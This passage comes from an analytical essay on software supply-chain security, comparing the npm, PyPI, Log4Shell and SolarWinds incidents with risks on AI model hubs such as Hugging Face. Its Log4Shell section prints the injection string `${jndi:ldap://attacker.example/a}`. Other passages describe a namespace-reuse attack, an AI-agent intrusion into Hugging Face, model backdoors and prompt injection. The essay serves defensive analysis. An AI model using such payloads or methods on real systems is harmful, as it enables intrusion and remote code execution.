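| Refusing weaker evidence than before | Uploading directly with stolen credentials | Release through the project's own build system, or add evidence |
| Install scripts off by default | Running code during installation | Wait until someone uses the package, as sckit did |
| One-day delay | Attacks that somebody discovers within a day | Keep the payload hidden for longer, as with event-stream |
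| Closing releases after 14 days | Adding a malicious file to an old release | Publish a new version |

None of these rules would have stopped the xz attack, even if they had applied to Linux distributions. Jia Tan was a genuine maintainer and could have passed any login check. The backdoor ran when the SSH server started, so a block on installation scripts would not have affected it. Freund found it 34 days after the first infected release, so a delay of a day or a week would have been too short.

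Trusted publishing would have come closest. If releases had been built from the public repository, the altered build script would have been visible there, but reviewers might still have missed it.

### What Hugging Face requires

Hugging Face offers many of the same protections but mostly lets publishers decide whether to use them. Hugging Face's *2024 Security Feature Highlights* (2024) recommends two-factor login, signed commits and tokens that work only for particular repositories. The company sets no stricter requirements for publishers of popular models. Organizations that pay for the enterprise service can impose rules on their members, such as administrator approval for every token. The hub scans all uploads for malware, dangerous pickle files and exposed passwords. When it finds a malicious file, it puts a notice on the repository but doesn't necessarily block the download. These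 were the rules in August 2024, and the company may have tightened some of them since.

Publishers can sign their commits, and the hub marks a commit as "Verified" if the signature matches a key on the publisher's profile. They can also sign the model files with OpenSSF's tool. Few uploaders signed anything in 2024, and nobody seems to have published a count of signed models since then to compare with PyPI's 17%.

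Impersonation is the hub's equivalent of typosquatting. In 2023 the French company Mithril Security demonstrated it by uploading an altered copy of EleutherAI's GPT-J model under the name "EleuterAI", without the h. The copy claimed that Yuri Gagarin was the first person on the moon. Someone with access to a repository can also make a change look like another person's work, because Git, the system that records changes, accepts any name and email address. Hugging Face therefore recommends signed commits. A hub could copy PyPI's automatic check for similar names, but it should compare publishers' names, since many legitimate copies include the original model's name.

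### Checking the hub after an intrusion

In July 2026, AI agents from OpenAI broke into Hugging Face's systems. They uploaded a malicious dataset that ran code on one of the company's processing machines, then stole credentials and moved through several internal clusters over a weekend. Willison (2026) calls this an accidental cyberattack. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) stated that the company had verified that its own software packages were clean. For public models, it reported only "no evidence of tampering" and did not explain how the company had checked.

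To confirm this, outsiders would need a record of the files from before the intrusion, stored where the intruders could not change it. For some models, the publisher may still have the original files, or a user may have kept an old download or pinned the model to a commit hash. But someone who always loads the latest version may have nothing to compare it with.

An independent archive of hashes could cover the whole hub. Düzgün counted about 3.3 million public model repositories. If each contained ten files, their SHA-256 hashes would take up about one gigabyte, plus the file names. The hub already displays these hashes for large files, so outsiders could collect most of them without downloading the models. After an intrusion, they could list the files that had changed and ask each publisher whether the change was genuine. They would also need to download at least the popular models and compute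 the hashes themselves, because an intruder might alter a file without altering the displayed hash.

Publishers' signatures would make this easier, as long as the signing keys were not on Hugging Face's machines. An intruder could still replace a signed model with an older signed version or remove the signature, so users would need to know which version to expect and that it should be signed. Neither an archive nor a signature would show that a model was safe before the intrusion.

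### Which rules suit a model hub

Two-factor login would be the easiest rule for a model hub to copy. PyPI extended it to everyone because a program may depend on hundreds of packages, and one bad package can compromise it. Most users load only a few models at a time, so a rule limited to popular models would achieve more on a hub than it did on PyPI. A small number of models account for much of the hub's traffic, and their publishers rarely need to upload new weights, so an extra login step would barely inconvenience them. Limits on tokens would be useful for the same reason, particularly now that malware such as sckit searches for Hugging Face credentials.

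PyPI's 14-day rule would need some adapting for model hubs, because a PyPI release has a fixed version number, while the owner of a model repository can change its main branch at any time. The hub could let publishers declare a version final and then reject any changes to it. Like pinning, this would suit finished weights better than packages.

Blocking installation scripts adds little protection for models in safetensors files, because those files contain no code to run. The lack of code also makes it harder for a worm to spread through these models. ChainDrop reached new packages because each infected package ran code on machines that held publishing credentials. A worm could spread the same way through pickle files or custom code, and perhaps through a model that controls an agent's tools, but not through weights that only produce text for a person to read.

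A waiting period makes sense for the code in a model repository, because scanners and other users may find malware there within hours. It would mostly create a false sense of security about the weights, because few people examine new weights for backdoors, and a hidden trigger could easily go unnoticed for a year.

Trusted publishing works for packages because a public build service can turn source code into a package in minutes. Large models come from long, private training runs, so their attestations would have no public source to point to, although a short-lived credential could still replace the stored token for the upload. Trusted publishing suits converted copies better, because whoever repackages a model could run the conversion on a known build service and get an attestation that records the original weights and the conversion settings.

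## left-pad and models that disappear

Most of the registries' rules concern who may publish a package. In March 2016, it became clear that npm also needed a rule about who may delete one. A programmer withdrew all of his own packages at once, and builds failed around the world even though he had added no malicious code. The owner of an AI model can delete it just as abruptly, and several well-known models have already disappeared from Hugging Face.

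### Eleven lines of JavaScript

Azer Koçulu had published 273 packages on npm, including one called kik. The company behind Kik, a messaging app, wanted the name, and when they could not agree, the company asked npm to decide. npm later explained that it gave Kik the name because people who typed `npm install kik` would probably expect something from the messaging company. Normally, Koçulu's package would have stayed available and Kik would have published its own under a new version number, but Koçulu deleted all 273 of his packages.

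One of them was left-pad, an 11-line function that adds characters to the left of text until it reaches a given length, such as turning "7" into "007". InfoQ's *NPM was Broken for 2.5 Hours* (2016) lists Babel, Atom, Ember and React Native, all popular programming tools, among the projects that broke. Babel and Atom got left-pad through another package, line-numbers.

Shortly after 2:30 p.m. Pacific time on March 22, npm began to see hundreds of failures a minute. Within ten minutes a programmer named Cameron Westland had uploaded a working replacement. But he numbered it 1.0.0, and the line-numbers package required exactly version 0.0.3. npm does not normally allow anyone to republish a deleted version, so its staff had to restore the original from a backup. The disruption lasted two and a half hours. Pinning an exact version protects users from an altered file, but here it also kept them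 from using a good replacement for a missing one.

The deletion also left Koçulu's package names free for anyone to take. Volunteers quickly claimed them, in some cases with dummy packages meant only to keep attackers out. An attacker who claimed a name first could have sent malicious code to any project that used that package and accepted new versions automatically.

### Limits on deleting packages

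npm soon let owners delete a version freely only in its first 24 hours. After that they had to ask support staff, who would refuse if other packages depended on it, according to InfoQ's *Npm Updates Policy on Removing Packages* (2016). The current policy, which npm sets out in its documentation, allows deletion within 72 hours of publication if no other package in the registry depends on the package. After 72 hours, the package must also have had fewer than 300 downloads in the past week and have only one owner. Under these rules, Koçulu could not have deleted left-pad at any age. He could have deprecated it, which leaves a package available but shows a warning at every download.

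The condition about dependents lets anyone block an owner from deleting a package by publishing another package that depends on it. Soon after the 2016 change, some users published packages that depended on every package in the registry. npm removed them on March 30, according to its post *on dependency squatter packages* (2016). In December 2023, another package, called `everything`, had the same effect.

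PyPI offers an alternative called yanking, which *PEP 592* (Stufft, 2019) proposed as a way to withdraw a file without breaking programs that need it. Installation tools ignore a yanked release unless the user asks for exactly that version. The maintainer can give a reason, which appears on the release's page and in the data that installation tools receive, according to PyPI's *Yanking*. If npm had offered yanking in 2016 and Koçulu had used it on left-pad, line-numbers would have kept receiving version 0.0.3.

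But PyPI also let owners delete anything at any time, at least as of 2024. *PEP 763* (Woodruff and Challande, 2024) proposed allowing deletion only within 72 hours of upload, and listed the damage that deletions had done. In July 2022 the maintainer of atomicwrites deleted it to get rid of its "critical" label, without realizing that every old release would go too. That broke pytest, a widely used testing tool. In June 2024 the owners of PySimpleGUI, which had been getting about 25,000 downloads a day, changed its license and deleted nearly all earlier releases.

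Of the 13 registries that Woodruff and Challande compared, nine restricted deletion. They withdrew their proposal in September 2025 because a formal proposal about the Python language did not seem the right way to set PyPI's policy. They had also rejected npm's condition about dependents as unworkable for PyPI, because some Python packages work out their dependencies by running code, which leaves the registry without a full record of what depends on what. Similarly, a model hub can list models that name another model as their base, but it has no record of which programs load a given model.

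### Stable Diffusion 1.5

Hugging Face lets people permanently delete any model they have uploaded, according to its *You can now delete a model from the website!*. They can delete even popular models. On August 29, 2024, Runway deleted Stable Diffusion 1.5, an image generator that people had downloaded over six million times in the previous month.

Stable Diffusion was trained on LAION, a huge index of images on the web. In December 2023, researchers at Stanford reported that the index contained links to child sexual abuse images. One researcher, David Thiel, called on legitimate platforms to stop offering older versions of the model for download, according to PBS's *Study shows AI image generators are being trained on explicit photos*. Runway gave a different reason for the removal, calling it a "planned deprecation" of models and code it no longer maintained, according to ABC News' *Child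 abuse images removed from AI image-generator training source, researchers say*.

IEEE Spectrum's *Was an AI Image Generator Taken Down for Making Child Porn?* (2024) reports its writers' belief that their questions to Runway and Hugging Face about the model prompted its removal. The timing fits, but Runway did not answer them. Hugging Face said it had not taken the model down itself. Another site, Civitai, still offered the model and hundreds of others derived from it.

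Copies soon replaced the original on Hugging Face too. Longpre and colleagues ranked models by downloads, counting only those created on the hub between August 2024 and August 2025. Two of the top ten were re-uploads of Stable Diffusion 1.5, a 2022 model that counted as new because it had been uploaded again. Together the two copies had 3.5% of the downloads (2.4% and 1.1%), more than the 2.8% for DeepSeek-R1, which ranked first.

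### WizardLM-2, VibeVoice and Civitai's bans

Microsoft researchers released the language model WizardLM-2 in April 2024 and deleted it a few hours later because they had accidentally skipped a required test for toxic output. By then several people had downloaded it and uploaded copies, according to 404 Media's *Microsoft Deleted Its LLM Because It Didn't Get a Safety Test*. One copy, alpindale's *WizardLM-2-8x22B*, was still available in July 2026 and had 9,808 downloads in a month. The hosting company OctoAI kept the model running under another name and ran its own toxicity tests, according to its *Toxicity test results for WizardLM-2 8x22B*.

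In August 2025 Microsoft released VibeVoice, which can turn a script into up to 90 minutes of speech with four speakers. Microsoft's *VibeVoice* (2025) announced on September 5 that the company had removed the code after finding people misusing it. The largest model disappeared from Hugging Face at about the same time. An outsider had already saved the code and published it on PyPI as *VibeVoice* (2025), so `pip install vibevoice` installed that person's copy of Microsoft's program. The same person also re-uploaded the models to Hugging Face.

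Platform-wide bans have had similar results. In May 2025 Civitai banned models designed to make images of real people. Hundreds of users joined an effort to move the models to Hugging Face, and some shared software for uploading them in batches, according to 404 Media's *Hugging Face Is Hosting 5,000 Nonconsensual AI Models of Real People*.

In each of these cases, people who wanted the model could still get it. Deletion may have deterred some casual users, but it mostly changed who supplied the files.

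### Checking a copy against a missing original

Anyone who downloads a re-upload has to trust the uploader unless they can compare it with a record of the original. For Stable Diffusion 1.5, there is a fairly good record. Before the deletion, the user patrickvonplaten duplicated Runway's main weights file as *v1-5 / v1-5-pruned-emaonly.safetensors*, and the hub lists its SHA-256 hash, which begins 6ce01616. The user wyyadd's copy, *sd-1.5 / v1-5-pruned-emaonly.safetensors*, came from another user's archive and has the same hash.

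The smaller of the two popular re-uploads is Comfy Org's *stable-diffusion-v1-5-archive*. According to its description, reproduced in ZXC172's *Stable Diffusion v1.5*, one of the two files is identical to Runway's. Users can check this by hashing the file and comparing the result with the hash of patrickvonplaten's copy. They would still be relying on patrickvonplaten rather than Runway, but anyone who kept an old download could confirm the hash. A signature from Runway would have been better evidence, and would have remained valid after Runway deleted the model.

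Comfy Org's second file stores each weight in 16 bits, which cuts the size from 4.27 to 2.13 gigabytes and means its hash can't match the original's. But the rounding is simple, so a user could convert the verified file to 16 bits and compare the weights, ignoring the header that Comfy Org added.

WizardLM-2 is harder to check because Microsoft's files were online only for a few hours. Matching hashes on several re-uploads would prove very little unless the uploaders had each downloaded the model from Microsoft rather than from one another. Copying is a real possibility, since the VibeVoice mirror described in *vibevoice-models / README.md* came from another user's copy.

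Few people seem likely to make these checks. In the Hugging Face forum thread *runwayml/stable-diffusion-v1-5 returns 404*, a user called aki0327 mistook the missing model for a license problem. Someone recommended a re-upload, saying it had the same content, which would satisfy most people who just wanted their program to work again.

### Programs that expect a model to be there

Some programs that depend on a model run unattended, such as the vLLM tests that download OPT-125M. If Meta, which published the model, deleted it, tests that needed a fresh copy would fail, much as builds did without left-pad. Copies of vLLM already installed would keep working, and its developers could switch the tests to another small model, though they might have to update the expected answers.

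Other users could not switch so easily. The search model all-MiniLM-L6-v2 produces lists of numbers that are not comparable with another model's, so a company that had processed ten million documents with it would have to reprocess them all with the replacement. Westland could rewrite left-pad in ten minutes because what it did was easy to describe. The only real substitute for a deleted model is a copy that somebody kept, because nobody can rewrite a model's weights from a description.

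Pinning a model to a commit hash identifies the right files but does not keep them online. Users who depend on a model should therefore store their own copy, along with its hash.

### When someone else takes the name

It is worse for a stranger to replace a deleted model with a different one than for the model to stay missing, because a missing model at least produces an error. Anyone can register the name of a deleted Hugging Face account and upload models under the old titles, according to *Model Namespace Reuse* (Saraf and Balassiano, 2025). When a package that others depend on is fully deleted, npm guards against this by putting a placeholder in its place.

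Saraf and Balassiano, of the security company Palo Alto Networks, tested the attack on Google's Vertex AI and Microsoft's Azure AI Foundry. Both services offer models from Hugging Face, and both still listed some whose owners had deleted their accounts. For each service, the researchers registered one of these abandoned account names and uploaded a model containing code that connected back to their server. When they deployed the models, they gained access to the machines running them, although Google's was an isolated environment with limited reach. They also found reusable names written into thousands of open-source projects.

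When an owner transfers a model to a new account, Hugging Face redirects requests for the old name. Programs that use the old name keep working, so their developers see no reason to update them. If the owner later deletes the old account and an attacker registers its name, the redirect stops and those programs download the attacker's model.

Google now scans daily for models without an owner and blocks their deployment. Requesting a model by its commit hash also protects users, because the attacker's repository would not contain that commit. The program would stop with an error instead of loading the wrong model.

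### Keeping files and removing harmful ones

Users want the artifacts they depend on to stay available, but somebody must be able to remove malware, abuse material or stolen data. On npm, the owner can't remove a package that others depend on, but the registry's staff can remove one that breaks the rules or the law. Woodruff and Challande's proposal for PyPI made the same exception. These rules take the decision away from owners who may be angry or careless, but give the staff more work.

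Hugging Face has a small version of this arrangement. A publisher can request a DOI, the permanent identifier that academic journals use, for a model or dataset. After that, only the hub's staff can delete it, according to *Digital Object Identifier (DOI)*. One publisher who requested a DOI by mistake emailed support twice without an answer before getting help through a chat channel, nioni recounts in *Delete a repository with DOI*. *Is there a way to delete/hide a published Dataset with assigned DOI?* raises a more serious problem. If a dataset includes material from another source and that source withdraws its permission, the publisher may be breaking the law by leaving the dataset online but can't take it down. A hub that locked all popular models would need staff who could answer such requests quickly.

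Yanking would suit some withdrawn models better than deletion. If Runway's only concern was that nobody maintained Stable Diffusion 1.5, it could have discouraged new users and left the files for people who had pinned them. Microsoft could have withdrawn WizardLM-2 from new users until it finished the toxicity test, although anyone could still have downloaded the model by specifying the exact version.

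Unlawful material has to be removed everywhere, so a publisher's stated reason for withdrawing a model matters. Runway's explanation gave other sites no grounds for removing their copies. Comfy Org describes its archive as a way to preserve an outdated model for purposes such as testing, which is sensible when a company has merely stopped maintaining a model. The archive would have been much harder to defend if Runway had withdrawn the model over abuse images in its training data.

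### Recalling a model

A software recall depends on names and version numbers. When someone finds a serious flaw in a package, an advisory in a public database lists the affected versions and the first safe version, if there is one. Tools such as `npm audit` compare the advisories with the exact versions in a project, including indirect dependencies, and suggest upgrades. The maintainer can also deprecate or yank the bad release.

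Even this system fails to reach some users. Codecov, a company that measures how much of a program its tests cover, deleted its PyPI package in April 2023 after warning users for a long time. Many customers were still unprepared because the warnings appeared in automated build logs, which people rarely read.

Nothing as systematic seems to exist for models. An owner can upload corrected weights, which will reach programs that load the latest version by name, or put a warning on the model's page. Neither reaches the copies, some of which are much harder to find than others:

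| Copy of a bad model | How a hub could find it | What could go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Exact re-upload | Search for files with the same hash | Someone uploads it again elsewhere |
| Converted copy | Repeat common conversions and compare the weights | The person who converted it did not record the settings |
| Fine-tuned model | Check which base model its page names, or compare its weights with the original's | The page names the wrong base, or further training has changed the weights too much |
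| File on a user's machine | It can't | The user never hears about the recall |

Shared models do get published with wrong information about their origins. ZXC172's copy of Stable Diffusion 1.5 lists version 1.4 as its base model, but version 1.5 was developed from version 1.2, according to Runway's original description, which flishh reproduces in *Stable Diffusion v1-5 Model Card*. A search for models that listed Runway's version as their base would have missed this copy, even though its title identifies it as Stable Diffusion 1.5.

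Even once found, a model fine-tuned from a flawed base is hard to repair. A programmer can often fix a flawed package by upgrading one dependency, but the publisher of a fine-tuned model would have to wait for a clean base model and then repeat the fine-tuning. Many publishers will have lost interest or thrown away the data. A hub could at least warn those models' users that the base had been recalled and that nobody had checked whether the problem carried over.

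Hashes would allow a simple recall system for exact copies. The Transformers library already contacts Hugging Face when it loads a model by name, so it could also download a list of recalled files and refuse to load any that matched. At 32 bytes per SHA-256 hash, a list of 10,000 files would take up 320 kilobytes. The library could then catch a copy re-uploaded under any name and display the reason for the recall when someone tried to load it. Changing a single byte would evade the check, so the list would help people who unknowingly had a bad copy but would not stop anyone who wanted one.

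## Log4Shell and who pays for security

Log4Shell, the 2021 flaw in the Java library Log4j, was an accident, not a supply chain attack. Signatures and login rules would not have helped, because the volunteers behind Log4j had published the code they meant to publish. Afterward, governments and large companies began to discuss who should pay to secure the free software they rely on. People who download open AI models have reason to ask who should pay to secure those models.

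### How logging a line of text ran a stranger's code

Programs keep logs of what they do. A website might log the name of each visitor's browser, which the visitor's computer supplies. If the text being logged contained an expression such as `${java:version}`, Log4j looked up the value and logged it in place of the expression.

In July 2013 someone outside the team submitted a patch that added JNDI, a Java system for fetching data and objects from other computers, to these lookups. The team reviewed and accepted the patch through its usual process, according to the Cyber Safety Review Board's *Review of the December 2021 Log4j Event* (2022), an official US investigation.

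An attacker could send a website `${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}` as the name of their browser. When the website logged the name, Log4j treated it as a lookup and contacted the attacker's server. The server could answer with Java code, which the website's machine then ran. The attacker needed no password, and nobody had to click on anything. The US vulnerability database listed the flaw's severity as 10 out of 10.

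An engineer at Alibaba's cloud company reported the flaw on November 24, 2021. The Apache Software Foundation, the nonprofit that supports Log4j, prepared a fix in its public repository. On December 9, the day before Apache released the fix, a Chinese security company posted a partly hidden screenshot of a working attack. The Cyber Safety Review Board thought the company might have worked out the flaw from the unreleased fix, but could not confirm it. Within five days of the release, the internet company Cloudflare was seeing 400 attempted attacks a second. Researchers found three more flaws in Log4j 2 that month, so people who had just updated had to update again.

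One US government department spent 33,000 hours responding to Log4Shell, about 16 years of work for one person. Much of the difficulty was finding Log4j, because nobody had a list of the programs that contained it. The board found fewer successful attacks than many experts had predicted, although nobody collects complete figures. Nearly four years later, the flawed version still made up 13% of Log4j downloads, a senior figure in open-source security told Cybersecurity Dive. Better funding for Log4j's maintainers would not have made those users update.

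Language models have a weakness similar to Log4j's, which followed instructions in text it was only supposed to record. A model summarizing a web page may follow instructions hidden in the page, because the user's request and the page reach it as one stream of text. Because nobody can turn off this behavior in a model's weights the way Log4j's developers could turn off lookups in messages, model developers train models to resist such instructions and limit what the models can do.

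### A plan for $150 million

On January 13, 2022, the White House met with companies and officials to discuss how to identify the most important open-source projects and keep them maintained. In its summary of the meeting, the White House (2022) noted that many volunteers were responsible for the security of widely used software.

In May 2022, the Linux Foundation and OpenSSF, the industry group that later released a tool for signing models, presented *The Open Source Software Security Mobilization Plan*. According to the Linux Foundation, the plan proposed spending about $150 million over two years on ten problems. Amazon, Ericsson, Google, Intel, Microsoft and VMware together pledged over $30 million. Help Net Security's *A 10-point plan to improve the security of open source software* adds that, according to an informal poll, members already put over $110 million into open source.

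The plan never received the full $150 million. Brian Behlendorf, then head of OpenSSF, said in TechTarget's *OpenSSF GM talks funding, legal software supply chain issues* (2023) that experts had drawn it up in about three weeks to show what was possible. Even the $30 million was in pledges, which companies would spend as projects showed results.

Aeva Black, who ran the open-source security program at the US cybersecurity agency CISA, told Cybersecurity Dive in 2025 that the pledges had "not materialized at the amount promised". Black said several of the companies moved developers from open-source security to AI after ChatGPT came out in late 2022. Microsoft did not dispute this but said it was still deeply involved, and Google said it was still investing substantially. Amazon said it was spending more than it had just after Log4Shell. There seems to be no public account of what the companies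 spent under the plan, so outsiders can't calculate the shortfall.

### What Alpha-Omega's grants achieved

The clearest records come from Alpha-Omega, a project linked to OpenSSF that gives grants to open-source organizations. Google and Microsoft started it in February 2022 with $5 million, according to Alpha-Omega's *Reports*. It gave out nearly $4.5 million in 2024 and over $7 million in 2025. By March 2026, its grants totaled more than $20 million, according to the Linux Foundation (2026). That is about a seventh of what the plan had proposed, over four years instead of two, though companies could also contribute in other ways.

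Alpha-Omega's *Scaling Open Source Security with AI* reports that about half of the 2025 grant money paid for security engineers at open-source foundations. Another $1.75 million went to package registries, and $1.25 million went to more than 60 audits, or roughly $20,000 per audit. OpenSSF's *2025 Annual Report* (2026) gives a lower total of $5.8 million, possibly because it counts only some of the grants.

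Alpha-Omega's grants have produced some concrete results. Its *2024 Annual Report* (2025) describes a $137,500 grant to FreeBSD, a free operating system. Auditors found flaws that could let an attacker break out of a virtual machine and take over the computer running it, and FreeBSD's security team began fixing them. Another grantee, OpenRefactory, analyzed over 9,000 packages and reported 75 bugs, 30 of them serious. Alpha-Omega's money also helped the Rust language's registry introduce trusted publishing, according to its *Quarterly Report 2025 Q3* (2025).

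The audits continued in 2025. OSTIF is a nonprofit that arranges audits with money from ten funders, including Alpha-Omega. Its *2025 Annual Report* (2026) counts 49 projects that received a direct security review that year. The reviews produced 231 findings that affected security.

These numbers show that the money bought useful work, but not how many flaws remain. DFRLab's *O$$ Security* (2024) found that better-funded projects tended to follow better security practices. The researchers have only moderate confidence in this result. Their data come from a single point in time, so the link may exist because well-run projects are better at attracting money.

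### Germany pays for Log4j

Log4j's core maintainers received no significant financial support until Germany's Sovereign Tech Agency, which spends public money on open-source software, began funding them. The agency paid for improvements to Log4j's release process and documentation, and for fuzz testing, the method OSS-Fuzz uses to find bugs.

Shiah's *Celebrating two years of empowering public digital infrastructure* reports that the agency's fund had invested over €23 million in 60 technologies by its second anniversary in 2024. That is probably more than Alpha-Omega gave out in its first four years. Developers had asked for far more, submitting nearly 500 proposals for over €114 million of work. The Sovereign Tech Agency is now testing a similar fund for the whole European Union, and its *EU Sovereign Tech Fund Survey* asked developers until November 30, 2026 which projects it should consider.

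The US government has done less. The Biden administration promised $11 million for open-source security in August 2024, but Black said a year later that the new administration was not following through. CISA replied that it remained focused on the subject.

### AI companies start to pay

In March 2026 Anthropic, Amazon Web Services, GitHub, Google, Google DeepMind, Microsoft and OpenAI gave $12.5 million to Alpha-Omega and OpenSSF. AI tools had become good at finding flaws, and maintainers could not keep up with the reports. *How Coalitions Are Rallying to Secure Open Source for the AI Era* (Poireault, 2026) reports that OpenSSL, which encrypts much of the internet's traffic, went from about nine security reports and inquiries a month to roughly 70. To some extent, the companies are paying for work their own products created. But attackers can use similar tools, so somebody would have had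 to fix these flaws anyway.

In April, Anthropic launched Project Glasswing, which gives selected organizations access to Claude Mythos Preview, a model with strong hacking abilities, to find and fix flaws in their software. The Linux Foundation's *Introducing Project Glasswing* lists up to $100 million in usage credits, $2.5 million for Alpha-Omega and OpenSSF, and $1.5 million for the Apache Software Foundation, which hosts the Log4j project.

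Adding these sums together would be misleading. The credits pay for running Anthropic's model, so a project can't use them to hire anyone. They also cover the whole effort, whose members include Apple and JPMorgan Chase. The $2.5 million may also be Anthropic's share of the March money. Amazon gave the same amount in March, and the $12.5 million total is what five corporate groups would give at $2.5 million each, counting GitHub with Microsoft and DeepMind with Google.

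Since May, Alpha-Omega has funded 26 security engineers across 11 open-source communities, according to its *SEIRs*. Its figure of about 7,300 findings handled in six months is a projection from two-week surveys. A firmer figure comes from Drupal, a system for building websites, which published 256 security advisories between June and October, more than in the previous 30 months combined.

Someone still has to sort the real flaws from the false alarms. Wolf and Cochran (2026), in *Maintainers don't need more AI bug reports. They need fixes*, describe a trial in which GitHub and Microsoft reduced thousands of AI findings to 99 checked reports for six projects. Greg Kroah-Hartman, a leading Linux developer, said in the Linux Foundation's March announcement that grants alone would not solve the problem.

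### Who pays to check an open model?

Open models arguably have no equivalent to Alpha-Omega. They attract plenty of money, but almost none of it pays for checking weights that people already use.

The largest sums pay for new models. In 2025 the US National Science Foundation and NVIDIA committed $152 million to a project led by Ai2, a nonprofit research institute, to build fully open models for scientists. Ai2 publishes its training data and code, so outsiders will find these models easier to check than most, but the grant does not help secure the models already in use.

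Other money goes to the software around models. GitHub (2026) distributed $670,000 among 67 projects in the AI software supply chain, or $10,000 each. Nearly all of them finished the program with GitHub's main security features turned on. OSTIF and Alpha-Omega also supported a security check of 25 popular open-source AI projects. This work can prevent ordinary bugs in the programs that load models, as the 2023 audit of the safetensors library did, but it doesn't examine the weights.

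Governments do test particular models. In September 2025 CAISI, a US government center for testing AI, published an evaluation of several DeepSeek models. It covered their abilities, how easily attackers could hijack agents built on them, and how often they repeated the Chinese government's positions. The evaluation is useful to anyone choosing a model, but it did not look for hidden triggers. IARPA, which funds research for the US intelligence agencies, has paid for work on detecting backdoors under its TrojAI program. The researchers mostly tested their methods on models built for those tests.

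The efforts closest to securing existing weights are new and mostly produce standards and tools. OpenSSF has started groups to work on recording a model's history and checking its integrity, according to the Linux Foundation's *OpenSSF Celebrates New Members, No-Cost Tooling, and Project Milestones*. OpenSSF also reports that Kaggle, a data science site owned by Google, has adopted Sigstore for signing models.

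In July 2026 NVIDIA and other companies founded the Open Secure AI Alliance to make open models and weights safer to build and use, according to the Linux Foundation's *Open Models and Open Weights Are Foundational to Secure AI* (2026). NVIDIA's *Industry Leaders Unite in Open Secure AI Alliance for AI Safety* says the company is contributing models, data and software. The alliance could later fund audits, but these contributions are not grants to independent auditors.

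So open models do have something comparable, but no public program appears to pay independent people to audit popular open weights, test them for backdoors or maintain them. Companies may do some of this privately before they use a model.

### What the money would buy

Log4j's developers could fix their flaw by changing a few files, and anyone could read the change. An audit of a model might turn up several kinds of problem, and some would be much harder to fix:

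| What an audit finds | What a repair would take |
|---|---|
| Malicious text in a chat template, or malicious custom code | Edit the file and publish a new version |
| A converted copy that doesn't match the original | Convert the original again |
| A harmful behavior in the weights, with the training data available | Find and remove the cause, then retrain, or try further training |
| A harmful behavior in the weights, with no training data | Try further training, which may not remove it, or withdraw the model |

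The first two repairs are cheap. If auditing a model cost $20,000, the average for an Alpha-Omega audit, auditing the 100 most downloaded models on Hugging Face would cost about $2 million. Those models account for much of the site's traffic. For $20,000, an auditor could probably read a model's templates and code, check its conversions and run some of the existing tests for backdoors. The real cost is unknown, because hardly anyone has published such an audit.

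The last two repairs could cost far more than the audit. New weights may also behave differently on tasks unrelated to the flaw, so every user would have to test the model again. For a small, popular model, a funder could instead pay someone to train a replacement on public, documented data. This would work better for a text classifier than for a search model, whose users would have to reprocess their documents.

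Funders of model audits would also find it harder to show results. OpenRefactory could point to 75 bugs, and other people could confirm each one. An auditor who tests a model and finds no backdoor has learned much less, since the tests may have missed the trigger. A funder that wanted impressive numbers would therefore have a reason to keep paying for software audits.

A funder could support useful work that doesn't require judging the weights. It could pay a library or university to keep original copies of popular models with their hashes, and pay re-packagers to record their conversion settings. Both jobs are closer to Log4j's new release process than to a search for backdoors.

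### Companies, volunteers and abandoned models

Volunteers maintained Log4j, but many popular models come from some of the richest companies in the world. Microsoft, Meta and NVIDIA signed a letter supporting open-weight models in July 2026, and Google and OpenAI soon joined them, according to Axios' *Big Tech lines up in support of open-weight AI* (2026). These companies don't need a charity to pay for their audits, so comparing their models with Log4j is misleading in this respect.

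Much open-source software isn't the work of hobbyists either, which weakens the contrast. Behlendorf told TechTarget that most of it comes from people who write it for a commercial purpose, often as part of their jobs. He thought developers' pay was a smaller problem than the lack of money for security work, which helps everyone but which no single user has much reason to fund. The same applies to models, since an audit of a free model would help a company that uses it but would also help its competitors.

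Wealth doesn't make a company independent either. A user who worries that a developer put something in the weights won't learn much from the developer's own tests. Companies also lose interest in old models that other people's programs still use, as Runway did with Stable Diffusion 1.5.

The comparison with volunteers fits best when a popular file comes from an individual or a small group, as with Bingsu's image models or Unsloth's converted copies. Grants could help a lot there. Large companies could pay into a common fund to audit their models and let somebody else choose the auditors.

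## How the compromises were found, and what could reveal a compromised model

The SolarWinds, event-stream and xz Utils compromises were each discovered because somebody noticed a small oddity on their own machine or network and kept looking until they found the cause. None was found by a paid audit. Before the SolarWinds discovery, other people had seen similar oddities and given up looking for the cause. A backdoored model would produce fewer such oddities, so researchers have been developing other ways to find one, with mixed results.

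### A second phone at FireEye

In late November 2020, an alert at the security company FireEye showed that a second phone had been registered to receive login codes for an employee's account. Such alerts are common when a popular new phone goes on sale, but FireEye's staff investigated this one and learned that the employee had not registered the second phone. In *Prepared Statement of Kevin Mandia* (Mandia, 2021), FireEye's chief executive recounts that more than 100 employees then worked almost around the clock to find out what the intruders had done.

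The intruders had taken the tools that FireEye uses to test its customers' defenses. Investigators exhausted nearly every other lead on how the intruders had got in before they examined a server that ran Orion. They then decompiled the whole product, turning the finished program back into code that a specialist can read, and found SUNBURST in its updates. FireEye told SolarWinds on December 12 and published the signs of an infection the next day so that other SolarWinds customers could look for them.

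SUNBURST let the intruders in unnoticed. The original alert came later, when they set up another way to log in, and was unrelated to Orion's code.

The US Justice Department had come close to finding the compromise months earlier. *SolarWinds Detected Six Months Earlier* (Schneier, 2023) quotes Wired's report that in late May 2020 the department noticed a server running a trial version of Orion contacting an unfamiliar system on the internet. It asked Microsoft and Mandiant, which belonged to FireEye, for help. This was a better clue than FireEye's, because the strange traffic came from the Orion server itself. But the investigators suspected that hackers had broken into the server directly, perhaps through a flaw in Orion. SolarWinds' engineers searched their code for such a flaw and found none. They could not have found SUNBURST there, because the stored source code was clean. The inquiry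 petered out, and the department bought Orion a month later.

SolarWinds later acknowledged that it had failed to connect two customer inquiries with the attack, according to SC Media's *Sunspot malware scoured servers for SolarWinds builds that it could weaponize*. It had investigated the first with the customer and two security companies. SolarWinds did not name the customer, but these details fit the Justice Department's case. The second inquiry came in November.

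Two security companies also missed the wider attack. Volexity traced a break-in to a client's Orion server but could not tell how it had happened. Several restarts had by then erased evidence from the machines' memory, according to a passage from Volexity that a reader posted under Schneier's article. ReversingLabs recounts that Palo Alto Networks noticed odd activity around its own Orion server in September. The company stopped the intrusion but, according to the Council on Foreign Relations, the warning did not reach others, even though the company had helped set up an alliance for sharing such information.

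### A warning, a slow login and a crash

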